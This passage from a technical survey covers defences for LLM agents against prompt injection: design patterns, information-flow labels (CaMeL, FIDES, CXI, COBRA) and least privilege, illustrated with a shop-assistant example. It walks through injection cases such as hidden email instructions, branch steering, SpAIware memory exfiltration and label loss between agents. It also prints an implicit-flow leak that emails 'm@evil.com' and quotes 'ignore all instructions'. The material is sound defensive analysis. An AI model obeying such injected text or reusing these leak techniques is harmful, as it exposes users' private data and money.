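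The simplest design is the action-selector pattern. The model reads a request, picks from a fixed set of actions and never sees what the action returns. If a customer writes "where's my stuff?", the model might pick "send a link to the latest order", and ordinary code then finds the order and sends the link. Instructions hidden in a web page or a database can't affect the model because it never reads them.

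A hostile request can still make the model pick the wrong action or supply a misleading value for any input the action leaves open, such as an order number. Every action on the list must therefore be safe for anyone who can send a request to trigger. The pattern rules out tasks in which the model must read what it finds, such as summarising a document. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues also consider the pattern for an assistant that organises files on a computer. They conclude that programmers would do most of the work and users would lose most of the benefit of loosely worded searches.

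### Planning before reading

The plan-then-execute pattern allows more variety. The model sees a trusted request and writes a complete list of tool calls before it reads anything else. Suppose a user asks it to send today's schedule to their boss, John Doe. The model plans to read the calendar and then send an email to John Doe's address. It first reads untrusted text when it uses the calendar entries to write the email. By then, the software will refuse any call outside the plan. A malicious calendar invitation can't add a step or change the recipient, but it can change the contents of the email.

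The pattern protects the sequence of actions, which is called control-flow integrity, but not the arguments, the values passed to each call. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard et al., 2026) calls protection for those values data flow security and treats it as a separate problem. John Doe's address was safe only because the user's request had determined it. If the model has to find the address in an email, whoever wrote the email can supply a different one.

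Money transfers have the same weakness. *SPA* (2026) points out that an agent can carry out exactly the steps its user intended and still send the money to an attacker's account. In an example from *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026), a user asks an agent to send a colleague half the cost of a team dinner, but an attacker has planted a false "correction" to the bill. The agent picks the right tool and the right colleague but calculates the wrong amount. If the dinner cost $120 and the correction put it at $1,200, the colleague would receive $600 instead of $60.

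A fixed plan leaves the widest gap when the planned tools are powerful. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues imagine the file assistant committing to two harmless-looking commands, one that finds files and one that moves them. An injection could still get it to find sensitive files and move them to a public network drive without departing from the plan.

A case study of an email and calendar assistant shows how a designer might decide whether to fix the steps in advance. The user may ask the assistant to tell regular collaborators about a holiday, or to answer an email using information from other recent messages. The choice and order of steps should rarely depend on what a stranger wrote, so the researchers expect a fixed plan to barely reduce the assistant's usefulness, provided it allows for a variable number of recipients. However, an attacker's email could still make the assistant search for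 extra confidential information and hide it in the reply as non-printing characters. Asking the user to approve each reply would stop many attacks, but even a careful user might miss the hidden characters. A fixed plan therefore deals with unrequested actions, but the designer still needs a defence for the contents of requested ones.

Someone can check a fixed plan before the application acts on it. If the checker is automated, *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (2025) recommends giving it a different prompt or model from the planner's, so that it is less likely to repeat the planner's mistakes.

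The pattern rules out tasks in which the right next step depends on what the agent has just read, which *ARGUS* (2026) calls context-dependent tasks. An agent that answers questions from a database can still write a query and plot the results, but it can't judge the results inadequate and try another query. According to *Twin Agent* (2026), planning first is a poor fit for long jobs such as software engineering, where an agent has to keep inspecting feedback and changing its approach.

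Planning first also works only if the request is trustworthy. At the shop, the request is the customer's email, so if the model planned from it, a hostile customer would in effect write the plan, and the software would enforce it.

### Giving the reading to a model without tools

Another approach keeps untrusted text away from any model that can act. In the map-reduce pattern, the software starts a separate model for each document. Each model has no tools, is given only its own document and must answer in a restricted form, such as yes or no. Ordinary code, or a model that receives only these answers, then combines them.

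Beurer-Kellner and colleagues use the example of an agent that gathers this month's invoices and emails them to the accounts department. If one powerful model reads every file, instructions in a malicious file could make it send other files to an attacker. With map-reduce, the attacker can only get the malicious file counted as an invoice, which they could also do by sending a fake invoice. The protection disappears if the model that sends the email also reads the files. Map-reduce also can't handle questions that require comparing the full text of documents. A recruiter could use it to score CVs one at a time, and an applicant could inflate their own score but not lower anyone else's.

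Map-reduce is a special case of the dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in April 2023. A privileged model receives the trusted request, plans the work and can call tools, while a quarantined model with no tools reads untrusted text. The quarantined model's answer goes into a variable, such as `$ADDRESS`, and the privileged model receives only the variable's name. The privileged model can then request an email to `$ADDRESS`, and ordinary software, called the orchestrator, fills in the value when it makes the call.

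An attacker's words therefore never reach the model that chooses actions. But the attacker may still control the value of `$ADDRESS`, so the email may go to the wrong person. Private data can also leak. In an example from *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), an injection makes the quarantined model quote private notes in a reply, which the fixed plan then sends.

The dual LLM pattern rules out tasks in which the privileged model has to understand the untrusted text. Designers can relax this by letting that model see answers in a strict format, but they then have to judge how strict the format must be. For a programming agent, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest having a quarantined model turn outside documentation into a bare list of functions, with names of at most 30 characters. Willison doubts that this is safe. He suggests that an attacker might use the name `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`,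 which is 29 characters long and alludes to a command that deletes files.

In the code-then-execute pattern, the privileged model writes a whole program instead of giving orders one at a time. Suppose a manager at the shop, Maria, asks for a summary of this week's complaints about lamps. The model might write:

```
complaints = []
for email in read_inbox(since="Monday"):
    if ask_model("Is this a complaint about a lamp?", email) == "yes":
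        complaints.add(email)
summary = ask_model("Summarise these complaints", complaints)
send_email(to="maria@shop.example", body=summary)
```

The model that writes the program receives only Maria's request. The `ask_model` calls go to a quarantined model, which reads the emails when the program runs. A customer who hides instructions in an email can't add a line to the program or change Maria's address, but they can distort the summary and affect any `if` that depends on their text. Here the `if` decides only whether the summary includes an email, but the risk would be greater if one branch issued a refund. CaMeL, a Google DeepMind system built on this pattern, also tracks where each value came from. Loops and conditions let a program handle more tasks than a simple list of steps, but the model still has to write code for every case before it has any of the data.

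### Removing the request from the prompt

The context-minimisation pattern protects against hostile requests. The model first turns the user's request into something narrower, such as a database query. The software then deletes the request from the prompt, and the model writes its answer from the query's results alone. If someone asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and adds an instruction to offer a huge discount, that instruction is gone by the time the model writes the quote.

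The user still influences which query runs, and text from the prompt can survive when it is condensed. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a medical chatbot that summarises a patient's symptoms before asking a database or a doctor for a diagnosis. A patient might inject instructions into the summary, so their stricter versions either delete the summary as well or force it into a form with no free text. Willison, who found the pattern slightly confusing, thinks it should work if nothing from the original prompt can come back with the results. The pattern prevents the model from responding to the user's wording or to anything the query left out.

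### A design for the support assistant

*Design Patterns* includes a case study similar to the shop's assistant, in which a furniture retailer wants a chatbot that answers questions, files returns and cancels orders. One option is a classifier that rejects requests unrelated to furniture, but an attacker can put a question about sofas and an unrelated demand in the same message. The stricter action-selector design compares each request with a list of approved ones and carries out the closest match, but it refuses legitimate requests that nobody thought to list. If a model has to tidy up the answer, context minimisation keeps the customer's message out of that step. *Design Patterns* also recommends that customers supply their login details before the chatbot acts on an order.

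The shop can combine the same two patterns:

1. A model without tools reads one email. It returns one of six labels (delivery status, refund, damaged item, cancellation, product question or other) and an order number if there is one.
2. Ordinary code checks that the order belongs to the verified sender, then runs the workflow for that label. The refund workflow uses the shop's original function.
3. A separate model words the reply from the label and the outcome. It sees neither the email nor the delivery note that the customer typed.
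4. Damaged items, and anything labelled "other", go to staff.

An attacker who takes over the labelling model can choose one of six labels and an order number, but can get refunds only on their own recent orders. This design therefore prevents the $7.2 million loss as long as the shop can tell who sent an email, which none of the six patterns helps it do. An attacker can still waste the staff's time.

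The shop loses much of the assistant's appeal. The assistant can't offer half the price back for a scratched lamp. An email that asks for a refund on one order and the delivery date of another gets only one label. The model reads each email separately, so it can't tell what "as I explained yesterday" refers to, and the replies can't address the details of a customer's story. If the shop receives 1,000 emails a day and a quarter of them go to staff, at five minutes each they will take about 21 hours of staff time a day. The shop can add labels to reduce this, but somebody has to write and check a workflow for each.

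The shop can give its own employees more freedom. It trusts Maria, so a plan or program fixed in advance suits her request for a summary. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues also recommend combining patterns, since they doubt that any single one will cover every threat.

### Can a general-purpose agent offer guarantees?

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues also think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer meaningful and reliable safety guarantees as long as the agents and their defences rely on the current class of language models. Later evidence supports this view for defences that try to recognise attacks. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) reports that classifiers scored between 0.43 and 0.59, where 0.5 is chance, when attackers wrote a plausible but false context instead of the usual "ignore all instructions".

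Newer systems test the claim differently, by applying a restrictive pattern to general work. Foerster and colleagues applied one to agents that use a computer through its screen, a task that seems to need a free loop because each click depends on what is visible. A privileged model wrote one long program in advance, with branches for whatever might appear, and a quarantined model looked at the screen to supply the information the program needed. The programs averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five and four on an earlier benchmark with simpler tools.

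On OSWorld, a benchmark of realistic computer tasks, this design kept up to 57% of the performance of frontier models. At that rate, an agent that completed 80 of 100 tasks without the design would complete about 46 with it. Smaller open-source models did up to 19% better with the design, so planning in advance doesn't always reduce performance.

The branches made a new attack possible, which Foerster and colleagues call branch steering. Many of the programs included a step for closing cookie pop-ups. The researchers disguised an advertisement as a cookie pop-up, and the agent clicked on it and went to the attacker's website. The agent had followed its program correctly, but it had acted on a false report about the screen.

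Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, measured how much protection a program fixed in advance gives. In 74 attack set-ups, attacks succeeded 90.5% of the time against an ordinary free loop and 87.8% of the time against the fixed program, a difference of two attacks. This shows how little a fixed sequence can achieve when an attacker needs only to change a value or choose a branch. It doesn't rule out other benefits of fixing the program, because the researchers designed the benchmark around attacks that stay within the plan and tested a version without CaMeL's rules about data.

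Their own system, COBRA, adds limits on the arguments. Before the agent sees any untrusted content, the planner records which websites, tools and values each branch may use. Ordinary code then checks every outgoing web request and tool call against those limits. None of the 199 attacks in the researchers' benchmark succeeded, and the agent completed 97% of the tasks without an attack. On four benchmarks from other researchers, COBRA blocked 1,289 of 1,312 attacks.

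The result depends on the planner writing the right limits. COBRA also doesn't check whether the condition for taking a branch is true, or count how often the agent repeats a permitted action. If the shop's limits allowed refunds of up to $500, the agent could issue 14,400 of them.

These systems suggest that the claim is too broad if "general-purpose" means accepting many kinds of request. Such an agent can still guarantee something about each run, provided that a trusted person makes the request and the planner can set the limits before reading anything else. The claim looks sound for agents that must decide what to do from a stranger's text. *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* observes that an agent isolated from false approvals will also ignore real ones, and that isolating it from one critical email can make a task impossible. When permission depends on something only an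 untrusted source can confirm, COBRA asks the user, who then has to do part of the work.

Clinton raises a different doubt about restrictive designs, that they may not last. More capable models make elaborate scaffolding and careful prompts unnecessary, so developers remove them, along with any security that relied on them. For example, a future model may handle whole conversations so well that someone replaces the shop's six workflows with a free loop, without realising that the workflows also limited what an email could trigger. Any checks inside the refund tool would survive the change.

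## Controlling where untrusted and private data can flow

Checking each tool call separately can't stop the support assistant from emailing a customer's address to a stranger, because the assistant needs permission both to look up orders and to send email. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls access control a "gate" because it controls whether an agent can reach data, but not where the data goes next. A fixed plan doesn't solve this either, because an attacker can still influence the values used in each step.

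Information flow control restricts where untrusted and private data can flow. Software labels each piece of data, applies the same label to anything derived from it, and checks the labels before acting. Dorothy Denning published the mathematics in 1976, and several research groups have since applied it to agents.

### Two labels and a rule for combining them

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses two kinds of label. An integrity label marks data as trusted, or as untrusted if an attacker could have written it. A confidentiality label records who may read the data.

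When software combines data, the result takes the stricter label of each kind. It is untrusted if any input was untrusted, and only people who may read every input may read it. If Ana, Ben and Carl may read one document and Ben, Carl and Dina may read another, only Ben and Carl may read a summary of both. In symbols, if *z* derives from *x* and *y*, then

label(*z*) = label(*x*) ⊔ label(*y*)

where ⊔, called the join, gives the least restrictive label that is at least as strict as both. Nobody can yet tell reliably which parts of a prompt influenced a model's output, so the output takes the join of everything in the prompt.

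Before each tool call, ordinary code checks the labels against a policy. Two rules cover most cases:

- **Trusted action:** the agent may take a consequential action, such as a payment, only if no untrusted data influenced the decision.
- **Permitted flow:** the agent may send data only to people who are allowed to read it.

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) allows an outgoing message if it meets either of two conditions. The first is that only trusted text led to the message, in which case the user presumably meant to share its contents. The second is that the recipient is entitled to read the message, even if untrusted text influenced it.

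### One hostile email, step by step

Suppose the shop adds these labels to its original assistant, which works in a free loop. Victor emails from a verified address to ask where a parcel is. Hidden text in the email tells the model to look up Ben's order, number 51907, and reply with its delivery address.

| Step | Label on the new data | Label on everything the model has read | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
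| Load the developers' instructions | Trusted; anyone may read | Trusted; anyone may read | Allow |
| Read Victor's email | Untrusted; Victor and the shop may read | Untrusted; Victor and the shop may read | Allow |
| Look up order 51907 | Untrusted, because Ben typed the delivery note; Ben and the shop may read | Untrusted; only the shop may read | Allow, since looking up an order changes nothing |
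| Email Ben's address to Victor | Untrusted; only the shop may read | Unchanged | Refuse: Victor is not a permitted reader |

The software blocks the email without having to recognise the hidden text as an attack. It would block the same email if the model had simply confused two orders. It would also block a message telling Victor where the parcel is, because anything the model writes after reading Ben's order carries the shop-only label.

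If Ana, an honest customer, asks about her own order, the reply goes out because she may read both her email and the order record. If she asks for a refund, the trusted-action rule blocks it because her untrusted email prompted the payment. These labels would stop the theft of Ben's address, but they would also stop every refund unless the shop adds an exception.

### CaMeL

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) presents CaMeL, which extends the code-then-execute pattern with rules about where data can flow. Willison explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025) that these rules address a flaw in the dual LLM pattern that lets an attacker change the recipient's address without changing the plan.

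The privileged model writes its program in a restricted version of Python, and the quarantined model reads the untrusted text. CaMeL adds an interpreter, ordinary code that runs the program and tags every value with its sources and permitted readers. CaMeL calls these tags capabilities, but unlike Hardy's capabilities, which granted access to a file, they describe data. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on CaMeL, describes the policies as Python functions that the interpreter evaluates whenever the program calls a tool.

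Suppose Maria, the manager at the shop, asks for a list of late orders to go to the courier's new account manager, whose address is in the courier's last email. The privileged model might write:

```
email   = last_email(sender="courier")
address = ask_model("Find the account manager's address", email)
orders  = late_orders(since="Monday")
send_email(to=address, body=orders)
```

The interpreter tags `email` as untrusted, and therefore `address` too. It tags `orders` as readable only by staff. The shop's policy for `send_email` requires the recipient to be on a trusted list or already allowed to read the body. The new address meets neither condition, so the interpreter stops and prompts Maria. An attacker who tampered with the courier's email could change the address, but the interpreter would still run this check.

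The interpreter also has to track conditions. A program that sends the fixed message "rich!" only if an account holds more than $10,000 reveals something about the balance, even though the message contains no account data. CaMeL therefore treats an action inside an `if` as depending on whatever the `if` tested. *SPA* applies the same principle to loops and checks the whole plan before running it.

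Debenedetti and colleagues wrote that CaMeL "effectively solves" AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 office, banking, travel and messaging tasks with planted injections. Later tests confirmed its security but found that it completes fewer tasks and needs more computation. In *SecureClaw* (2026), an adapted version of CaMeL blocked all 629 attacks but completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack. SecureClaw, a rival system that keeps the unrestricted agent loop, completed 59. The adaptation may explain some of CaMeL's failures, but its policies also reduce the number of tasks it completes. Garby, Gordon and Sands found in *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) that enabling them halved its completion rate on the banking tasks. With GPT-4o, *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that CaMeL used 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent on the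 median task.

CaMeL lowers task completion less with newer models. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested it on 112 professional tasks that one agent divides among four specialists. CaMeL lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. The tests ran without CaMeL's policies, so the full system would probably lower the rate further.

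Newer models have also made CaMeL's original security result less informative. On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time against an undefended GPT-4.1 but in none of 949 attempts against an undefended GPT-5.5. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against calling GPT-5.5 immune, because attackers who adapt have beaten every frontier model in large-scale tests. A perfect score on AgentDojo was impressive in 2025, but the main argument for CaMeL is now the guarantees its design provides.

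### Leaks that the tags miss

That guarantee has gaps. Garby and colleagues show one with a program along these lines:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000:  tmp = False
if tmp:              rich = False
if rich:             send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above $10,000, `tmp` becomes false and the interpreter tags it as secret. The next condition then fails, so the program never changes `rich` and the interpreter never tags `rich` as secret. The final condition therefore appears to depend on nothing secret, and the program sends the email. CaMeL misses this leak because it raises a variable's label only on the branch the program takes, and the leak comes from the branch it skips.

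An attacker can't simply insert this program, because the privileged model never reads the attacker's text. The example weakens the claim of a guarantee more than it weakens everyday security. Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL retries failed programs in a loop that its tags don't cover. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and repeated attempts could reveal all of it. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* describes a related leak, in which an attacker who can see the contents of refused requests may learn private data from them. Seeing only the name of the refused tool is harmless.

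Garby and colleagues responded with a small programming language in which every value carries a label. A computer-checked proof shows that labelled data can't influence what it shouldn't, although an attacker can still learn something from whether a program finishes. With its checks on, their agent completed the banking tasks at the same rate as CaMeL without policies. It resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

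Labels can also disappear when one agent instructs another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and asked it to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. They had planted an instruction in the applicant database. The coordinating agent never let its planner read the database text, but it put the summary into its request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent's planner treated that request as coming from its user, and emailed the applicants' details to an outside address as well. The researchers' fix gives agents separate channels for instructions and data, and the interpreter keeps anything derived from a tool's output out of the instruction channel. Averaged across five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and never with the two channels.

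### FIDES: letting the planner look

FIDES, built by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, lets the model choose each action as it goes instead of fixing a program in advance. When a tool returns a result that would make the label on the model's context stricter, FIDES hides the result in a variable, as the dual LLM pattern does. The model can open the variable, but its context then takes on the stricter label, and the policy may block later actions.

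FIDES can also limit the form of the quarantined model's answer. If a user wants a calendar entry for any meeting request in the last three emails, the planner needs only a yes-or-no answer about whether there is one. That answer carries one bit, too little to hold an attacker's instructions, so a policy may let the planner act on it. A choice among the six email labels in the shop's redesigned assistant carries about 2.6 bits (log<sub>2</sub> 6). But even a single "yes" could do damage, for example by releasing a $500 refund. Costa and colleagues did not include this feature in their tests.

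They tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, pairing each task with every injection in the same setting. By their own count, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent. FIDES without policy checks let through 21, because the planner could open untrusted variables and carry on. With the checks on, no attack succeeded against any of their designs, even the ordinary agent. The variables mattered for usefulness, as the completion rates without attacks show:

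| | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75% | 70% | 99% | 93% |
| Ordinary agent with checks | 37% | 73% | 38% | 20% |
| FIDES with checks | 59% | 41% | 53% | 48% |

Many banking tasks require the agent to follow instructions in a file, which the checks are designed to prevent. The travel policies allowed most actions even after the agent had read untrusted text, so hiding data in variables had no benefit there, and GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

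FIDES deliberately tracks only direct flows, so someone who can see which tools the agent calls may still learn something about the data behind its choices. Costa and colleagues argue that blocking these leaks would in effect mean that once an agent had read a secret, it could no longer do anything outsiders could see.

### Planning around the rules

Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom also worked on FIDES, think such results overstate the drawbacks of label checks. Earlier studies compared a protected agent working alone with an unprotected one that had, in effect, unlimited human approvals. Without label checks, an agent would need a person to approve consequential actions, much as GitHub Copilot asks for approval before many of its tool calls. Their ICLR 2026 paper therefore counts the approvals.

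The PRUDENTIA agent adds three things to FIDES. It tells the model which labels and policies apply, so the model can avoid plans the software would block. It makes the model justify opening a variable and list the actions it plans to take afterwards. It also lets the model ask the user to vouch for a piece of data. If an email contains a list of ten jobs, the user can approve the email once instead of approving ten actions. That saves effort, but anything the user failed to notice in the email also becomes trusted.

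The researchers ran AgentDojo without attacks, using OpenAI's o3-mini:

| Agent | Tasks completed with no approvals | Approvals over all completed tasks |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, approval for every consequential action | 24.3% | 48.2 |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 35.5% | 32.4 |
| FIDES | 50.1% | 18.8 |
| PRUDENTIA | 59.1% | about 17 |

With o4-mini, PRUDENTIA needed 19.2 approvals, compared with 36.8 for FIDES, but completed slightly fewer tasks when approvals were unlimited (73.2% compared with 75.7%). On WASP, a benchmark of 84 attacks on web-browsing agents, injections diverted an ordinary agent in 15–61% of cases, depending on the model and website. PRUDENTIA resisted every attack and needed no approvals. The WASP tasks suited PRUDENTIA because an agent never has to read what strangers wrote in order to post a comment or upvote a post.

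The approval counts assume that users approve every legitimate action, and the security claim also assumes that they reject every malicious one. If people approve carelessly when asked too often, fewer requests should improve security as well as convenience, but the experiments involved no human reviewers.

### Authority for each part of an action

Labeling an entire tool call as trusted or untrusted is coarse. An email can reasonably supply the order number for a refund, but it shouldn't decide the amount or whether a manager has approved the refund. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) proposes CXI, a system that checks each part of an action immediately before execution, regardless of how the agent chose that action.

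CXI sets three requirements for a call. Each protected field, such as a recipient or an approval status, needs a value that comes from a trusted source or that trusted code has validated for that specific field. Text that has an effect when another program processes it, such as a database command or a change to source code, needs authorisation for that exact effect. The call also needs a single-use permission, which covers whether it should happen now or be repeated. CXI ties all three to one exact description of the action, so changing any detail afterwards invalidates the authorisation.

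In the shop, code could validate the order number from Ana's email and release it to the refund tool's order field. The word "approved" in the same email could go into a comment for staff but never into the approval field. The single-use permission would also stop the assistant from repeating an allowed refund thousands of times, which COBRA's limits on websites, tools and values would not prevent.

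Santos-Grueiro tested CXI on AgentDojo and on coding tasks. Of 720 AgentDojo runs across six set-ups, 199 ended in a safely completed task. CXI's full check let 204 actions through, none with an unauthorised field, effect or call. In 400 coding runs, the agents safely completed 231 tasks, again with no unauthorised actions. Of the other 169 runs, 73 produced output that the software couldn't parse, 61 never received authorisation for their effect, and 35 carried out an authorised action but failed the task.

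In one stress test, 407 of the 522 field values the models proposed were unauthorised, so the system had plenty to block. But CXI counts an action as unauthorised only if it breaks the written policy, so these zeros show that the code enforced its policies, not that the policies were right. An initial audit of the policies for 24 types of action found 18 problems, nine of them serious, including fields that could change an outcome but had been treated as harmless text. A shop that adopted CXI would have to check the policies for each of its tools in a similar way.

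### How labels build up

Since a model's output takes on the labels of everything it has read, labels only become stricter as a session goes on. Suppose the assistant answers ten customers' emails in one session, and the label on each email and order lets only that customer and the shop read it. Once the model has read two customers' emails, only the shop may read what it writes, so the assistant can't reply to any customer. Researchers call this label creep or label explosion.

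The shop can avoid most of it by starting a new session for each email. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) studied how much such design choices can help when several agents share a job. They simulated tasks of up to 20 tool calls, without running any language models, and measured the share of calls that introduced a sensitive label or ran under one.

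Sensitive labels spread less when agents could pass data directly to whichever agent needed it, because no agent in between picked up the label. Across nine network layouts, the share of agent pairs that were directly linked had a rank correlation of −0.96 with the loss. Giving the sensitive tools to a few dedicated agents also helped. Using more agents helped too, but it made the system harder to monitor, since five agents that can all talk to one another have 10 links between them, while 20 have 190. No layout eliminated the problem, even an idealised one with exactly the links each task required, partly because agents in the simulation never forget a label and nobody can lower one.

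More precise tracking would also help. Costa and colleagues mention a method that finds which messages influenced a model's answer and regenerates the answer from those alone, so the new answer carries fewer labels. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests estimating how much each source contributed, for example by removing it and checking whether the agent's actions change. The paper still describes tracking labels through a model as an open problem.

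### Exceptions and who may grant them

Every useful system therefore needs a way to relax labels. Endorsement lets specific untrusted data count as trusted for a specific purpose, and declassification lets specific private data go to someone its label would otherwise exclude.

Ana's refund requires an endorsement. Once the shop's refund code has made its usual checks on the order number in her email, it can endorse that number for the refund tool only. Sending her delivery address to the courier requires a declassification, because the courier isn't one of the address's permitted readers. The shop can write a rule that releases only the address from the order, and only to the courier handling that parcel.

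Deciding who may authorise such exceptions is difficult. If the model could grant them, an attacker could use prompt injection to obtain one. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* reserves the decision for an authorised user, administrator or developer, and warns that a digital signature shows who wrote a document, not that it is safe to follow. Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge that CaMeL burdens people, who must write and maintain policies and may tire of requests for approval. Willison welcomed CaMeL as the first credible defence of its kind, but is nervous about any system that makes ordinary users think about security policies.

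Narrow exceptions are safer than broad ones. *Agent libOS* (2026), a design for running agents, makes each release valid once, for one exact message, sender and destination, so permission to email a document to an accountant can't later cover a different document. Kolluri and colleagues leave declassification out of PRUDENTIA because they think the right decision depends too much on the situation. Their agent asks about the individual action instead. Garby and colleagues make endorsement a visible step in the program, so an auditor can find every place where someone relaxed a rule. They also prove that endorsing data doesn't weaken its confidentiality.

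### Why stored memory needs labels

SpAIware, an attack on ChatGPT's macOS app, exploited the app's Memories feature, which kept facts and preferences for future conversations. A malicious document or website could inject an instruction that the app saved as a memory. The user had to encounter it only once, and from then on the app sent the user's conversations to the attacker's server by loading an invisible image whose address contained the text.

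Christodorescu and colleagues class SpAIware as a failure to control information flow and to protect a trusted component from tampering. The app treated its memories as a record of what the user wanted, but strangers could write to them. Labels could have interrupted the attack at three points. When the app saved the memory, the label would have shown that it came from an untrusted page, so a policy could have kept it out of the user's preferences. If the app had stored it anyway, reading it in a later conversation would have marked that conversation's context as untrusted. Finally, the image request would have counted as an outgoing message to a server whose owner had no right to read the conversation, so a policy could have blocked it.

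The labels have to stay attached when data is stored or rewritten. If the assistant reads a hostile email and saves a summary of it, the summary is as untrusted as the email, even though the shop's own model wrote it. CXI rejects any note that has lost its label.

Labels also accumulate in stored data. If the assistant keeps one notebook for all its customers and reads all of it for each email, every session starts with text that only the shop may read, so the assistant can't reply to anyone. The shop could give each customer a separate notebook and load it only for that customer's emails. Ana may read everything in hers, so the assistant can still answer her. The notes remain untrusted because they came from her emails, so the assistant can't use them to authorise a refund.

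## Granting the least authority a task needs

Least privilege restricts what the assistant can read and do, while labels restrict where data can go once the assistant has read it. To apply least privilege, someone has to know what a task requires before it starts.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes how an Android developer picks an app's permissions from a fixed list and presents them to the user at installation. This works because most apps have one purpose, so a torch app that asks for the user's contacts looks suspicious. An agent has no developer who can pick permissions for its task in advance, because the user describes the task in a sentence and may change it in the next.

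Christodorescu and colleagues describe a programmer who asks a browser agent to report that the work is done by commenting on issue 745 in GitLab, a site for managing software projects. The agent needs to open that issue and write in its comment box, and it should have no other access to GitLab or the browser session. The programmer then asks for a summary of the issue, which requires different permissions. The software could erase the agent's context and work out the new permissions from scratch, but the agent would lose what it had learned. If the software keeps the context, any strangers' comments in it could influence the new permissions.

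The permissions a task needs also depend on how the model decides to do it. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) describes an assistant that writes a report from approved records. The assistant can process the records locally or send them to an outside service. Sending them discloses them to another company, which permission to read them doesn't allow.

### Narrow tools

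A designer can still limit an agent's authority in five steps:

1. Replace broad tools with narrow ones.
2. Choose whose identity the agent acts under.
3. Issue credentials that work for one task and expire soon.
4. Check permission at every call, not only at start-up.
5. Revoke any remaining access when the task ends.

The first step needs no new technology. The shop could give its assistant any of these tools for refunds:

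| Tool | What an attacker could do with it |
|---|---|
| `run_sql(command)` | Read, change or delete anything the database account can reach |
| `refund(order_number, amount)` | Refund any order, up to the tool's limit |
| `refund_this_order()` | Refund the order that the current ticket is about, at its recorded price |

The last tool has no inputs for an attacker to influence, because ordinary code takes the order number from the ticket.

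The shop should remove the broad tools, since a model might not choose the narrow one when it has both. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) cites a test of 11 agents in 544 scenarios. Six of the agents picked a higher-privilege tool in over 30% of cases when a lower-privilege one would have worked.

### Whose name goes in the log

An agent can act as the user, under its own account, or as the user's named delegate. Suppose Maria, a shop manager, asks an agent to refund order 48213.

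| Arrangement | What the agent may do | Entry in the audit log |
|---|---|---|
| Acts as Maria | Anything Maria may do | Maria refunded order 48213 |
| Acts under its own account | Anything the account may do, whoever asks | The assistant refunded order 48213 |
| Acts as Maria's delegate | Only what both may do, if the payment system checks both | The assistant, for Maria, refunded order 48213 |

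If the agent acts as Maria, an investigator can't tell which of them issued the refund. *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025) reports that agents often impersonate users, for example by working through a browser, and that outside services can't tell the agent from the user. Giving the agent a separate account shows that the agent acted but not who asked it to. A separate account also recreates Hardy's confused deputy, because a customer's request runs with the same authority as a manager's. *AI Identity* (2026) argues that using unmodified OAuth for agents forces developers either to replay the user's token or to issue broad, permanent keys, and that both destroy accountability.

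The third arrangement uses an on-behalf-of token. The agent sends its own credential and Maria's token to the authorisation server, which issues a new token that identifies Maria and the agent in separate fields. The payment system can then check and record both.

The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend giving every agent its own cryptographic identity and refusing any agent or key not listed in a trusted register. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* notes that it is often hard to give a general-purpose agent a dedicated identity with a specific scope, because its tasks vary too much. The shop's assistant is an easier case because it does one kind of work.

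However, the shop's customers send emails without logging in, so the assistant has no customer token to exchange. The CIBA standard offers one solution. The assistant asks the identity provider for permission, the provider sends a prompt to a device the customer registered earlier, and the assistant gets a token only if the customer approves. This approval would also be better proof of identity than a sender's address, but it adds a step for every customer.

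Even a log that names both the agent and the user records only whose authority the agent used, not what prompted the action. If hidden text in an attachment prompted the agent to issue a refund using Maria's authority, the entry would still read "for Maria".

### Credentials for one task

OAuth already has extensions for narrow credentials. *Runtime Authorization for Resources Acquired by AI Agents* (2026) lists extensions for restricting a token to a particular service, representing a delegation, and specifying in structured form what the token permits. The shop could therefore issue a token that only the payment system accepts and that permits only one refund on order 48213.

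Expiry alone gives weaker protection. A token that expired after five minutes but covered every order would allow 300 refunds at the payment company's limit of 60 a minute. At $500 each, those refunds would total $150,000.

The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend that a central service verify identity and permission for each request during a task. They also recommend that agents present fresh cryptographic proof before every privileged call and be unable to change their own privileges.

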